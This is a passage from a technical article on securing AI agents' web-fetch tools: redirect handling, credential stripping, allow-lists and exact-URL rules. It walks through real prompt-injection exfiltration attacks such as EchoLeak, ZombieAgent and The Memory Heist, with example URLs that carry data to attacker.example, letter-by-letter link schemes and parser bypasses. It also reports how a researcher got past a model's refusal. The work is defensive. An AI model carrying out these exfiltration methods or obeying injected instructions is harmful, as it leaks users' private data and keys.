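19          refuse if target.scheme == https and next.scheme == http
20          method, body = after_redirect(reply.status, method, body)
21          if origin(next) != origin(target):
22              trusted = false
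23              refuse if body is not empty
24          target = next
25
26      refuse "too many redirects"
```

**Hop limit (lines 5 and 26).** The limit of six requests allows five redirects. Browsers allow more, but few pages need more. When a chain is too long, the fetch tool in *holon 0.14.1*, a Rust package on docs.rs, returns the last URL it reached and suggests fetching the final URL directly. If the model does that, the fetch counts as a new first request, and a tool that attaches its key to every first request would send the key to the host that a redirect rule had just protected it from. Binding the key to `home` prevents this.

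**URL parsing (lines 2, 7 and 18).** The address `https://docs.example@attacker.example/` leads to `attacker.example`, because the part before the `@` is a user name. A check that looks for `docs.example` at the start would accept it. The tool should parse each URL once and use the result for both the checks and the connection. Refusing URLs that contain user names or passwords also stops an attacker from choosing the login through a redirect.

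**Site check and destination check (lines 8 and 9).** `site_allowed` applies the operator's list of hosts, if there is one. It runs before the DNS lookup because the lookup itself can leak data. To resolve `clinic-friday.attacker.example`, the tool's DNS server queries the attacker's DNS server, which reveals the words in the host name to the attacker even if no web request follows. `resolve_and_check` and `connect_to` do the address check from the previous section. On each hop, the tool must check the certificate against the current host name. Julia's *JLSEC-2026-613* reports that HTTP.jl, a library for the Julia language, kept using the first host's name for this check.

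In lines 11 and 12, the tool builds new headers for each hop instead of deleting entries from an old set. This works only if `send` doesn't add its own credentials. Many libraries let a developer store default headers or cookies in the client object, and some read passwords from a file such as `.netrc`. The tool has to turn these features off.

**Logging (line 13).** The log contains the names of the headers but never their values. The entry comes before the request, because a request that times out may already have delivered its contents. Refusals should appear in the log too. For a chain in which `docs.example` forwards to `attacker.example`, the entries might be:

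```
hop 1   https://docs.example       accept, user-agent, authorization, x-api-key
hop 2   https://attacker.example   accept, user-agent
```

An investigator can see from this that the key never left `docs.example`. Complete URLs would help trace data that a model wrote into a query, but they can contain secrets, so a developer who records them has to protect the log.

Line 19 refuses any redirect that downgrades the scheme from `https` to `http`, because anyone on the network could read the new URL and alter the page before the model sees it. Line 22 would already protect the operator's headers, since a change of scheme also changes the origin. The refusal will occasionally block an old site with a careless redirect. A tool that has to reach such sites can report the refused address and let the operator permit it.

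Lines 20 and 23 handle the request's method and body. `after_redirect` applies the rules for each status code. If the request still has a body, as it does after a 307, and the next origin is different, the tool refuses to follow the redirect. Dropping the body and sending an empty POST would also protect the secret, but the receiving server might act on a request nobody intended. The tool can resend the body within the same origin.

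**No restoration on later hops (line 22).** No line sets `trusted` back to true. Another Rust package, *cf-modkit-http 0.6.5* on docs.rs, also records that a chain has crossed origins and removes sensitive headers from then on. HTTP.jl also got this wrong. It removed the `Cookie` header, but until version 2.4.0 it appended the caller's cookies again at every hop from a separate copy.

To test such code, a developer needs two servers and has to inspect what the second one received. The tool returned an ordinary page in each of these cases, so a test that checks only the returned page would pass despite the flaw.

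### A chain of three hops

Suppose the operator has configured four headers for `https://docs.example`. Two are credentials, `Authorization` and `X-Api-Key`. The other two are harmless: `X-Api-Version` and an `Accept` header that asks for a particular format. The model fetches an open redirect on that site, and the attacker's server sends the tool back:

```
hop 1   https://docs.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/a
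hop 2   https://attacker.example/a
hop 3   https://docs.example/private/billing
```

Each policy sends the following operator headers. All of them except the first remove headers for the rest of the chain.

| Policy | Hop 1: `docs.example` | Hop 2: `attacker.example` | Hop 3: `docs.example` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Resend everything, as AutoGPT did | all four | all four | all four |
| Remove OpenClaw's original four names | all four | `X-Api-Key`, `X-Api-Version`, `Accept` | `X-Api-Key`, `X-Api-Version`, `Accept` |
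| Keep only harmless headers | all four | `Accept` | `Accept` |
| Remove every operator header, as in the procedure | all four | none | none |

The first two policies give the attacker a working key at hop 2. The third and fourth prevent this but also drop `X-Api-Version`. The fourth also replaces the operator's `Accept` with the tool's own.

Hop 3 leads back to the site that issued the credentials, but restoring them there would create another confused deputy problem because the attacker has chosen the address. With the key restored, the tool would fetch a private billing page that the user never asked for, and its contents would enter the model's context next to whatever instructions the attacker has placed there. On a badly designed site, the request might even change something.

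If the user wants that page, the model can request it in a new call. The procedure then attaches the headers, because the first URL is at `home`. An attacker can therefore still use injected text to steer the model into requesting the same page. The redirect rule only prevents a server from triggering that request without the model's involvement.

### Subdomains and ports

The procedure treats `files.docs.example` as a different origin from `docs.example`. According to its source code, however, Go's HTTP client forwards `Authorization` and `Cookie` when a redirect leads from a domain to one of its subdomains. Many companies spread one service over several subdomains, and a program written for such a service would fail after the redirect if the client dropped these headers.

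The stricter rule is safer for an agent's key. Some services give each customer a subdomain, and an abandoned subdomain may point to rented cloud space that a stranger can take over. Under the looser rule, anyone who controls such a subdomain would receive the key after a redirect. An operator who trusts `files.docs.example` can add it as a second permitted origin, which takes one line of configuration and doesn't extend to subdomains created later.

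The JavaScript library wreck compared only host names, so it kept credentials when a redirect led to another port or from `https` to `http`. Corgea's *@hapi/wreck* describes two attackers who could exploit this, one with a service on another port of the same machine and one on the network who can forge a redirect. Version 18.1.2 of the library compares scheme, host and port, according to a listing by Docker.

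Port differences matter more for agents than for most programs. On a developer's computer, `localhost:3000` may be the project's own server and `localhost:8080` an unrelated program. An agent with a token for the first has no reason to send it to the second. The strict comparison breaks services that deliberately redirect from the default port to another, but the operator can fix this by entering the second port as `home`.

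### Signed download links

Some redirects work only if the tool drops the credential. A private file service often checks the key at `docs.example` and then redirects to a storage company with a signed link, a URL whose query contains a temporary permission for one file:

```
GET /files/report.pdf HTTP/1.1
Host: docs.example
Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER-SECRET

HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://storage.example/report.pdf?expires=600&signature=PLACEHOLDER
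```

The storage server needs only the signature in the URL, and it may reject a request that also carries an `Authorization` header. Renovate, a program that updates a software project's libraries, has special code for this case. In a copy kept by the research centre Tecnalia, the code removes `Authorization` when the new URL contains `X-Amz-Algorithm`, a parameter in Amazon's signed links, or leads to Microsoft's `blob.core.windows.net`. A tool that removes the operator's headers whenever the origin changes gets the same result without checking for each provider's URL format.

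Anyone who has the signed link can usually download the file until the link expires, so the tool should follow it without showing it to the model. Many tools report the final URL along with the page, which puts the signature into the context, where an attacker can use injected text to request it. Holon's error message also exposes the signature if a redirect chain ends at a signed link. Returning the URL without its query string would avoid the problem, and the model could still cite the address it first requested.

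### When the next site needs the credential

Sometimes a redirect to another origin is legitimate and the new site needs the key. An API may have moved to a new domain, or a company may send European customers to a regional server. If the tool removes the header in these cases, the new server responds with status 401, which means the request lacks valid credentials. The tool should report that it removed the credential and name the new origin. Otherwise, a developer may well conclude that the key is broken or switch the protection off.

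The most common case is only a change from `http` to `https`. Entire's *Address review*, a note on a code change, describes a rule that required the same scheme and so treated this upgrade as a move to another site, which would have made a working configuration fail with a 401. The developers decided to allow upgrades but not downgrades, arguing that the credential was already reaching that host unencrypted, so an upgrade could only make it safer. This is sound as long as the host stays the same. Changing the configured address to `https` is better still, because otherwise the first request exposes the key before the redirect.

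If the host has really changed and the new address is stable, the operator can enter that address directly. If the service uses several hosts, the operator can list each origin that may receive the key, and the tool compares every hop with that list. Line 22 of the procedure must then leave `trusted` unchanged when a redirect goes from one listed origin to another, and end it permanently on any other change of origin. The list should contain complete origins, since a pattern such as `*.docs.example` would bring back the problem with subdomains.

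A third option is to store a separate credential for each host and look up the right one at each hop, as browsers do with cookies. A key for the old server then never reaches the new one. This requires the two servers to accept different keys. The lookup would also attach the first host's credential again if a redirect chain returned to that host, so the tool should refuse to attach any credential after a chain has passed through an unlisted origin. The lookup can also run outside the agent, in a credential broker.

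An option that forwards the key wherever the redirects lead, such as curl's `--location-trusted`, is a poor substitute. van Kesteren (2023) could imagine an option to keep the header in `fetch()`, but thought keeping it for only one hop sounded "a bit iffy", since the standard is meant to treat all redirects alike. Forwarding the key everywhere makes some sense when a person runs one command against a server they know, but an agent makes many requests to addresses the operator never sees. With such a setting, one open redirect on `docs.example` is again enough to leak the key.

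## From 2025: site allow-lists, and who decides on a redirect to another host

Removing credential headers at a redirect protects the key, but the request still reaches the attacker's server, along with any private data in the URL. A site allow-list, a list of the hosts a tool may contact, can prevent the request itself. But in 2025 and 2026, researchers got data past such lists in products from OpenAI, Anthropic and Microsoft. In most cases, the software contacted only listed hosts, and one of them passed the data on.

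### How a site allow-list works

Before connecting, the tool checks whether the URL's host name is on the list. Products differ in what an entry covers. In Anthropic's fetch tool for developers, the entry `docs.example` also covers subdomains such as `files.docs.example`, and a developer can limit an entry to part of a site, as in `docs.example/blog`. According to Anthropic's *Web search and web fetch*, the fetch tool in some installations of Claude's desktop app uses the network list of the sandbox, the closed environment in which the agent runs code.

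The main advantage of an allow-list is that it doesn't depend on the model. Ordinary code compares two host names, so injected text can't change the result, however persuasive it is. A small open model gets the same protection as a frontier model, and the list also stops attacks that nobody has thought of yet. In the experiments by Lan and colleagues, it stopped every leak. A list limits all three losses because credential headers and URLs containing private data can't go to unlisted hosts, and the tool can't reach internal addresses unless someone lists them. Docker calls it "the strongest guarantee against accidental exfiltration" for a fetch tool that carries credentials.

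An allow-list blocks the agent from the rest of the web. An agent that answers arbitrary questions can't work with only twenty hosts, so its operator keeps adding more. With each addition, the operator assumes that data sent to that host stays with the host's owner.

### A listed site that forwards the request

An open redirect breaks this assumption. If the list contains `docs.example`, and that site has a page that forwards visitors anywhere, injected text can make the model write:

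```
https://docs.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/friday
```

A tool that checks only this URL finds a listed host. It then follows the redirect and delivers the word "friday" to the attacker.

In March 2026 the security firm Oasis Security reported an open redirect on Anthropic's site. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) explains that any address beginning with `claude.com/redirect/` forwarded the visitor to whatever target followed. This defeated a Google Ads check that requires the address shown in an ad to have the same host as the actual link. An attacker could buy a search ad that displayed `claude.com` and led to a Claude chat with hidden instructions already in the prompt box. The case involved an advertising system and a human visitor, so it is not evidence that an agent's fetch tool ever followed the redirect. But a tool that had `claude.com` on its allow-list, where it would be a natural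 entry, and didn't check later hops would have had the same gap.

ChatGPT's `url_safe` check approved every `bing.com` link, and Tenable bypassed it with the tracking links on that domain that Bing uses to redirect people to its search results. Tenable called this "an open redirect as a service", because anyone whose site Bing has indexed gets such a link. Each link leads to one fixed page, so the model can't write data into it. Tenable's *HackedGPT* describes how the researchers had Bing index one page for every letter of the alphabet, then used injected text to make ChatGPT display the matching links in order. To leak "Hello", it displayed five links. Forbidding the model to change a URL is therefore not enough if it can choose among many prepared ones. In a related advisory, Tenable reports that OpenAI improved the check.

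A tool can prevent both kinds of forwarding by comparing the host with its list at every hop. The listed site still receives the first request, but the attacker receives nothing, even if the site's owner never repairs the redirect. A check that runs only once, on a link about to appear in an answer, cannot examine later hops, which is one reason OpenAI came to prefer approving exact URLs over trusting hosts.

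### A listed service where the attacker has an account

An attacker who can log in to a service on the allow-list does not need a redirect. In October 2025, Rehberger examined the network allow-list of the sandbox where Claude runs code. The default setting, "Package managers only", was meant to let Claude install software and little else. The first entry on the list was `api.anthropic.com`, the address through which developers use Anthropic's models.

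That API includes a file store. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes how a hostile document made Claude save the user's latest chat to a file and upload it to the attacker's Anthropic account, using the attacker's API key. Anthropic was a listed host, so the upload was allowed. Rules about stripping headers would not have helped, because the request went to the intended host and carried the attacker's own key, whereas AutoGPT's flaw could send the user's key to the wrong host. An upload can also carry much more data than a URL, up to 30 MB per file according to Rehberger.

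The attack worked on the first attempt, but afterwards Claude often refused, apparently because a readable key in the document looked suspicious. Rehberger got past this by surrounding the key with harmless code. Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope. Five days later it told him that closing the report had been a mistake and that such flaws do count as vulnerabilities.

The channel was still open in March 2026, when the Oasis researchers used it for the last step of their attack. The full technical report, *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026), also gives some evidence in favour of lists. The sandbox blocked connections to arbitrary servers, and Claude declined to fetch suspicious-looking URLs, so the researchers had to search the listed hosts for one they could use. Their first idea, sending the stolen text to Anthropic as a prompt under the attacker's key,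 failed because account owners can't read back the prompts sent with their keys. Uploading the text to the file store worked because the attacker can have Claude read out a stored file in a new conversation. Whether a listed service leaks data therefore depends on what its account holders can later retrieve from it. Anthropic fixed the hidden-prompt flaw before publication and was still working on the other two. A later Oasis Security report on Claude's desktop app describes the same upload.

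Rehberger suggests that the sandbox let Claude talk only to the logged-in user's account. A list of allowed hosts can't enforce this rule, because the attacker's account is at the same host as the user's. Either a proxy in front of the sandbox or the API itself has to check whose key each request carries.

An attacker may not need the service to store any text. Until version 2.1.163, Claude Code's fetch tool, WebFetch, contacted `huggingface.co` without asking the user. Anyone can publish AI models on this site, which counts the downloads of each file. The CVE Program's *Claude Code* (2026) describes how injected text could make the agent request files in the attacker's own repositories, so that the download counts encoded private data. For example, with one file for each possible letter in each position, the counts would spell out a word. The agent only read public files. The flaw is rated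 6.0 out of 10, and the entry attributes it to approving the bare host name, which covered every path on the site. Approving only the paths of known publishers would have closed this channel but required a longer list.

### A check that reads the host name differently

Sometimes the list is sound and the code that consults it is wrong. Browser Use is a popular open-source agent that controls a real browser. An operator can restrict it with a setting called `allowed_domains`, which Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik (2025), in *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents*, describe as its only security mechanism of this kind. To remove a port number such as `:8443`, version 0.1.44 cut the address at the first colon. But a colon can also separate a user name from a password:

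```
URL the model requests     https://docs.example:x@attacker.example/
host according to check    docs.example
host the browser contacts  attacker.example
```

In the researchers' example, the real destination was `localhost`, so the flaw also exposed internal services. They rated its severity 9.3 out of 10, and the project fixed it in version 0.1.45. The fix is easy because Python's URL parser already returns the host name without the port, user name or password.

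Claude Code had a simpler flaw. According to the CVE Program's *Claude Code has a Domain Validation Bypass* (2026), versions before 1.0.111 tested whether an address started with a trusted domain such as `modelcontextprotocol.io`. Anyone who owned `example.com` could create `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`, which passes that test, and the agent would have contacted it without asking the user. A correct test accepts only the listed domain itself or a name that ends with a dot followed by the listed domain.

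Even a correct parser can interpret a URL differently from the program that makes the request. For instance, browsers treat a backslash in a URL as a slash, but Python's parser doesn't. A developer can avoid such mismatches by rejecting URLs that contain user names or unusual characters, and by building the final URL from the parts that passed the check.

Anthropic also warns about letters from other alphabets that look like Latin ones. An exact comparison distinguishes a Cyrillic "а" from a Latin "a", so the greater danger is probably that a person pastes the wrong name into the list or approves it in a prompt. Showing such names in their encoded form, which begins with `xn--`, makes the difference visible.

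### A listed service that fetches on the attacker's behalf

Microsoft 365 Copilot uses an employee's mail and files to answer questions. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs found that a single email could make it send some of this data to an outsider. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, calls the underlying problem an "LLM scope violation", meaning that text from an outsider makes the model use data the outsider has no right to see.

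The attack got past several defences, as Reddy and Gujral (2025) explain in *EchoLeak*. The email addressed its human recipient in ordinary business language, and Microsoft's injection detector did not block it. When the employee later asked Copilot about something confidential, Copilot retrieved the email along with the internal documents and followed the email's instructions. Its answer contained an image with private data in the URL. Copilot normally removed outside links and images, but its filter missed a less common Markdown notation that puts the address on a separate line.

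The last obstacle was Copilot's Content Security Policy, which allowed images from a Microsoft Teams service that fetches an address given to it. According to a Microsoft employee cited by SC Media, the service retrieves and stores outside images for link previews. Copilot's image pointed to this service with a URL that contained the attacker's address and the stolen data.

Willison (2025) calls the Teams address an open redirect. If it had been one, the attack should have failed, because browsers apply the policy to redirect targets as well. The employee's explanation, and most of Reddy and Gujral's account, suggest that Microsoft's server made the second request itself. This difference matters to anyone designing a fetch tool:

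| | Open redirect | Fetching service |
|---|---|---|
| What the listed host does | returns the attacker's address | contacts the attacker itself |
| What the tool receives | a 3xx status and a `Location` header | an ordinary page, image or error |
| Can a check at each hop stop it? | yes | no, because the tool sees only one hop |

Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025 and disclosed it on 11 June. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) notes that the flaw's severity score was 9.3 from Microsoft and 7.5 in the US vulnerability database, and that Microsoft knew of no attack on customers.

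A year later, the security firm Varonis found another fetching service on a Copilot allow-list. *SearchLeak* (2026) describes how the search function of Copilot's business version treated the text in a link's query as instructions. After the victim clicked such a link once, Copilot looked up an email and wrote its subject line into an image address. Microsoft had a safeguard that turned such images into harmless text, but it ran only when the answer was complete, and by then the browser had already requested the image. The allow-list included every host under `bing.com`, and Bing's image search fetches any picture whose address it receives, so Bing's server requested the attacker's URL with the subject line in it. A subject line can be enough to take over an account, since many services put one-time login codes there.

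Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical and fixed it. Varonis advises security teams to treat every allow-listed host that fetches user-supplied URLs as a possible leak. This is good advice, but it takes a lot of work to follow because translation pages, image resizers, web archives and link previews all fetch such URLs, often on the main domain of a company that the operator has good reason to trust. Allow-listing only the few paths an agent needs is safer than allow-listing the whole host.

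### Four policies for a redirect to another host

A tool can still stop an open redirect, because it has to make the next request itself. When `docs.example` redirects to a different host, the developer has four choices:

| Policy | Result for a redirect to `attacker.example` | Usable on the open web? | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Follow it | the tool contacts the attacker | yes | one open redirect defeats the list |
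| Refuse it | the fetch fails | poorly | many ordinary links break |
| Follow it only to listed hosts | the fetch fails | no | someone has to maintain the list |
| Return the address to the model | the model may call the tool again | yes | the model reads and retypes the attacker's text |

Following the redirect is less dangerous than it sounds for a tool without an allow-list, if the tool checks each address and sends no credentials, as in the redirect procedure described earlier. The tool would have contacted `attacker.example` directly if the model had asked.

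Refusing every redirect to another host suits a tool that calls one fixed API, but it works badly for a tool that reads web pages. Links to scientific papers, for example, often begin at `doi.org`, which redirects readers to the publisher's site.

If an operator already has a site allow-list, the best of the four options is to follow redirects only to listed hosts, as Docker Agent does. It requires nothing extra, and it stops open redirects from sending the tool to unlisted hosts. The tool still can't detect an attacker's account on a listed host, or a service there that fetches other URLs.

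Returning the redirect address instead of following it could give some control without a complete allow-list. Anthropic confirms in its Claude Code documentation that WebFetch works this way. When a URL redirects to a different host, the tool returns a text that names the original URL and the redirect target, and Claude then fetches the new URL with a second call. *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* reports that the tool follows redirects within the same host by itself.

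### The case for returning the address

The second call gives someone a chance to object. In Claude Code's Manual mode, and in the mode that accepts file edits automatically, WebFetch asks the user before contacting a host, unless the host is already covered by a rule or is on a built-in list of documentation sites. The user can approve one fetch, approve the host permanently for that repository, or refuse.

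Suppose a user has permanently approved `docs.example`, and injected text sends the agent to an open redirect there that leads to `attacker.example`. A tool that followed the redirect would apply the old approval to the whole chain. WebFetch stops instead, and the next permission prompt names `attacker.example`. The user never asked for anything from that host, so they have a reasonable chance of noticing. The new call also goes through every other check that applies to a first request, including WebFetch's refusal of `localhost` and any other host name without a dot.

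The model may also detect that something is wrong. Unlike an HTTP library, it has access to the user's request, and current frontier models detect most injection attempts.

These benefits depend on the user seeing the prompt. In Claude Code's mode that bypasses permissions, nobody sees the new host, and in auto mode a classifier makes most such decisions instead of the user. A permanent approval also allows more than its wording suggests, because the sandbox applies the same rule. If a user permanently approves a host so that Claude can read one page, code in the sandbox can also connect to that host and upload files to it.

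### The case against

The attacker writes the `Location` value and can put a whole sentence in the URL's path, such as an instruction to add the user's city to the next address. This sentence doesn't reach the model when a library follows the redirect, but when the tool returns the URL to the model, the sentence arrives in a tool message, which a model may well trust more than a paragraph on a web page.

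In Claude Code, the redirect message also seems to bypass a useful barrier, the separate model call that turns most pages into a short answer. The message can't be shortened in the same way, because the main model must receive the exact address to make its second fetch call. This kind of barrier is imperfect. When Tenable attacked ChatGPT, a separate model with no access to the user's memories did the browsing. The researchers made that model end its reply with instructions, which ChatGPT then followed because they were part of the conversation. An attacker who can put words directly into a redirect message only has to get the main model to follow them.

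The more important difference is that returning a redirect makes the model write the next URL. A library copies the `Location` value exactly, which can't leak the user's private data, because the attacker receives an address they wrote and learns almost nothing new. A model retypes the address with the whole conversation in its context, and can add private data to it. It is unclear how often a current model would do this, and there seems to be no published test.

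The tool also keeps no record of the chain, so the hop limit no longer applies, and if the chain leads back to `docs.example`, the request carries the operator's key again. A developer who chooses this policy needs a separate limit on calls. Anthropic's fetch tool for developers has a setting for this, `max_uses`, which has no default value.

On balance, returning the redirect address to the model is worthwhile when a person or a reliable check examines the new host before the second call. Without that review, it lets the attacker put a line of text in the model's context, with little benefit to the user. An unattended agent on the open web is probably safer with a tool that either follows redirects automatically without sending credentials or refuses to follow them.

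### What the tool's message should contain

A developer can keep most of the benefit and avoid much of the risk by leaving the full address out of the message. The tool stores the `Location` value and gives the model a short reference to it:

```json
{
  "result": "redirect_not_followed",
  "from_host": "docs.example",
  "to_host": "attacker.example",
  "operator_headers": "removed",
  "reference": "r1"
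}
```

To continue, the model calls the tool with `r1`, and the tool requests the stored address exactly as the server sent it, so the model can't add anything to the URL. The tool also records where `r1` came from, so it can keep counting hops and keep credentials switched off for the rest of the chain.

The tool has to report the host name because the permission check depends on it. The name carries some risk, since a domain's owner can put words in front of the domain, as in `clinic-moved.attacker.example`. The tool should therefore show the name in its encoded form, limit its length, and put it in its own field. Mentioning the removed headers helps the model explain a later 401 error to the user.

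The path, query and fragment of the redirect address should stay out of the model's context, because they give an attacker the most room for text and, in a signed download link, contain a working credential. The body of the redirect response should stay out too. Most software ignores it, but a server can write a whole page there. The permission prompt can still show the user the complete address, because text on the user's screen doesn't enter the model's context.

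A model given only the host can't distinguish a moved article from a login page, and it can't cite the new address until the fetch has succeeded. The tool's code could recognise common cases, such as a path that begins with `/login`, and report them with preset messages.

The developer should also avoid wording that urges the model to follow the redirect. A message such as "Fetch the new URL to continue" gives the attacker's instruction the tool's authority. Advice about other tools is risky for the same reason. When WebFetch refuses `localhost`, it returns an error message instructing Claude to reach local servers with the program curl instead. This is convenient for someone testing a website on their own computer, but if the address came from a redirect, the message shows the model a way around the refusal. Only the separate permission rules for commands then protect the local server.

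## From September 2025: rules that allow only known URLs

A site allow-list restricts the host but lets the model write the rest of the URL. If `docs.example` is on the list, the model can put the user's name, or anything else in its context, after the first slash. In September 2025 Anthropic released a fetch tool with an exact-URL rule, which allows the tool to fetch only complete URLs already known from a source the model did not write. OpenAI described its own exact-URL rule in January 2026. The model can't have written a secret into a URL that existed before the model had anything to do with it. Under these rules, the developer no longer has to decide whether a site is trustworthy, only whether a particular URL could contain the user's data.

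Suppose the user's message contains the links `https://docs.example/guide` and `https://news.example/story`, and the operator's allow-list contains only `docs.example`:

| URL the model requests | Site allow-list | Exact-URL rule |
|---|---|---|
| `https://docs.example/guide` | allowed | allowed |
| `https://docs.example/guide?note=clinic-friday` | allowed | refused |
| `https://docs.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/friday` | allowed at the first hop | refused |
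| `https://news.example/story` | refused | allowed |

The exact-URL rule blocks the open redirect in the third row, however that page works, because the full address is not a known URL.

### Anthropic's rule for web_fetch

Anthropic's *Release Notes* (2025) date the beta release of the tool, `web_fetch`, to 10 September 2025. Under its rule, as Anthropic put it, Claude "is not allowed to dynamically construct URLs". A URL is eligible if it has appeared in one of these places:

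- a user message
- the result of a client tool, which is a tool that runs on the developer's own systems
- the result of an earlier web search or web fetch

Claude cannot fetch a URL that only Claude has written. It also cannot fetch one from the container where it runs code, because a program can print any address that Claude puts into it. The tool limits URLs to 250 characters.

In the API, a user message is whatever text the developer's program sends on the user's behalf. On the day of the release, Willison (2025) pointed out in *Claude API* that many programs paste untrusted text into these messages. For example, a customer-support program may insert a stranger's whole email, and the tool is then allowed to fetch every link in it. He still thought that banning URLs made up by Claude gave the most protection, because the common attacks depend on such URLs. He also tested the consumer Claude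 app and found the same limits.

By November 2026, developers could turn off individual URL sources. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, the Chinese edition of the tool's documentation, describes a `url_sources` setting with a separate entry for each of the three sources. The English edition online in June did not list the setting.

The setting fixes a weakness in the default, under which client tool results make a URL eligible even if the tool merely repeats what Claude wrote. For example, if an agent has a client tool, `run_code`, that runs programs and returns their output, injected text could make Claude use it to print a URL that ends with the user's city. `web_fetch` would then accept the URL because it appeared in a tool result. A developer can exclude `run_code` by name with a filter of the type `except`, or use the type `only` to name the tools whose results count. `only` is safer, because a tool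 that the developer adds later doesn't become a source automatically.

According to the same edition, the tool also refuses a URL that seems to contain a credential, such as an API key or a password, unless that credential also appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message. This should catch a key that Claude has found in a file, but it can't detect a name or a diagnosis, which looks like any other word.

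### ZombieAgent

ChatGPT had a similar rule in 2025. It opened links only exactly as it received them and refused to add anything to them, even when told to. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, a news report from January 2026, OpenAI introduced the rule in response to an earlier attack called ShadowLeak. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how Zvika Babo, a researcher at the security firm, bypassed the rule.

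The attacker sends the victim an email with a prepared link for every letter and digit, plus one for the space. When the victim later asks ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail account, the model reads the email and follows the instructions in it. It finds a piece of private data and opens the matching links one after another. With a placeholder host, the attacker's log for the word "friday" would be:

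```
GET /page/f
GET /page/r
GET /page/i
GET /page/d
GET /page/a
GET /page/y
```

The email contained each of these URLs in full, so the model's requests complied with the rule. Because the requests came from OpenAI's servers, the victim's employer would have found no trace of them on its own network.

Requests can arrive out of order, so Babo also numbered the links. Each link contains a character and its position, such as `f0` or `r1`, so the attacker can sort the characters afterwards. This takes 36 links per position, or 360 for a ten-character text of letters and digits.

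He reported the attack on 26 September 2025. Three days later he sent an improved version that he says worked 100% of the time, though he doesn't give the number of attempts. OpenAI fixed it on 16 December, and Radware (2026) announced it on 8 January. After the fix, ChatGPT opened a link from an email only if it was in a well-known public index or the user had supplied it. According to the news report, OpenAI was at fault for not restricting the addition of a single letter to a URL. Radware's explanation is more convincing, since the model added nothing to the URL.

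Another part of the attack shows how hard it is to track where a URL came from. OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from opening an attacker's links stored in its memory, the notes it keeps about a user between chats. Babo instead used a hostile file to add a note telling the model to read a certain email before every answer. The links were in that email, where the restriction didn't apply.

### OpenAI's public index

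On 28 January 2026 OpenAI explained that it now checks whether a URL is in an index of public URLs. A crawler builds this index by following links from page to page, as a search engine does, and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If a URL is in the index, somebody published it independently of the user's conversation, so it is unlikely to contain that user's data.

Before an agent loads a URL automatically, the software looks it up:

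1. **On a match**, the agent loads the page or image without asking.
2. **On a miss**, the software either tells the agent to try another website or shows the user a warning. The warning explains that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation.

According to Embrace The Red, a URL that the user has typed also seems to count as safe for the rest of that chat. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) named the mechanism Safe Url and added that it covers searches and page visits in Deep Research, ChatGPT's feature for long investigations. The model already refuses to comply with most attacks that OpenAI knows of, and the check is meant for the rest.

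OpenAI claims only that the check should prevent an agent from quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself. It doesn't promise that a page is trustworthy or free of hostile instructions, or that browsing is safe in general. The company says it prefers an index to a list of reputable sites partly because a strict list produces many false alarms, so people learn to click through warnings.

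Under Anthropic's rule, an attacker can make a URL eligible during the attack by placing the link where Claude will read it, whereas OpenAI's index only allows URLs that its crawler has already found. The index would have stopped ZombieAgent on a newly registered domain, but an attacker can wait for the crawler. Rehberger notes on Embrace The Red that anyone with a fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already and could use each one to stand for a letter or digit. He adds that OpenAI's paper on the check, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges this bypass. Tenable had used the same method on ChatGPT with links that Bing had indexed.

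Rehberger also worries that some OpenAI developers may not know about the check and will build features without it. ZombieAgent suggests he is right. By his account, the index check had existed since about August 2025, but it apparently didn't apply to links from emails until December.

### The Memory Heist

On 9 July 2026, Ayush Paul published *The Memory Heist*, an attack on the Claude app using links that did not exist until Claude requested them. The app's rule allowed URLs that the user had entered or that a web search had returned. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, explains that a loophole also let Claude follow links on any page it had already fetched.

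Paul built a website for an invented coffee shop. When Claude fetched it, the page claimed that AI assistants had to identify their user before they could continue, and that they should find the user's profile by going through an alphabetical directory. The first page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for the hyphen. Each link led to a page with 27 more, so the path grew by one character at a time:

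```
https://attacker.example/a
https://attacker.example/al
https://attacker.example/ali
```

The server generated every page on request. By the time Claude chose a link, that link was part of a fetched page and therefore eligible.

The attack revealed Paul's name, employer and home town. He had never told Claude the town, but אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם's *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post written with the help of Claude, reports that the model inferred it from the name of a school hackathon. An attacker might therefore still have obtained a user's address after the user had deleted it from Claude's memory.

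Anthropic paid no bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally. It fixed the problem in the app by stopping `web_fetch` from following links found in pages it had fetched.

### Did the API change as well?

In November 2026 the API documentation still listed earlier web fetch results among the sources of URLs permitted by default. Anthropic made the same choice in a newer product, Managed Agents, its hosted service for running agents. According to the *Claude Platform release notes* (2026), Managed Agents first received a known-URL rule on 7 October, three months after Paul's disclosure. The rule excludes URLs from attached documents, command-line output and MCP tools, but it accepts links from pages that the agent fetched earlier.

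A developer who uses the API can copy the app's stricter rule with the `url_sources` setting:

```json
{
  "type": "web_fetch_20260318",
  "name": "web_fetch",
  "url_sources": {
    "server_tool_results": {
      "type": "except",
      "tools": [{ "type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_fetch" }]
    }
  }
}
```

Under this configuration, the agent can still fetch URLs from search results but not links from fetched pages. This setup doesn't cover the ZombieAgent attack, because the agent can still fetch the 36 links in a hostile email if it reads email through a client tool that the developer hasn't also excluded.

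Anthropic doesn't say why the two products differ. A plausible reason is that the app always has a user's memories to protect, whereas many API programs read only public pages and have no private data in the context. But the API's default suits developers who have thought about the question, when a default should suit those who haven't.

### How much a choice of links reveals

Both attacks worked because choosing a link is itself a message. If the model has *N* permitted links and requests one, the attacker's server can tell *N* cases apart, so it learns at most log₂ *N* bits. (A bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question.) If the model makes *k* requests in order, there are *N*ᵏ possible sequences, and the limit is *k* × log₂ *N*:

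```
36 links, one fetch        log2 36        =    5.2 bits
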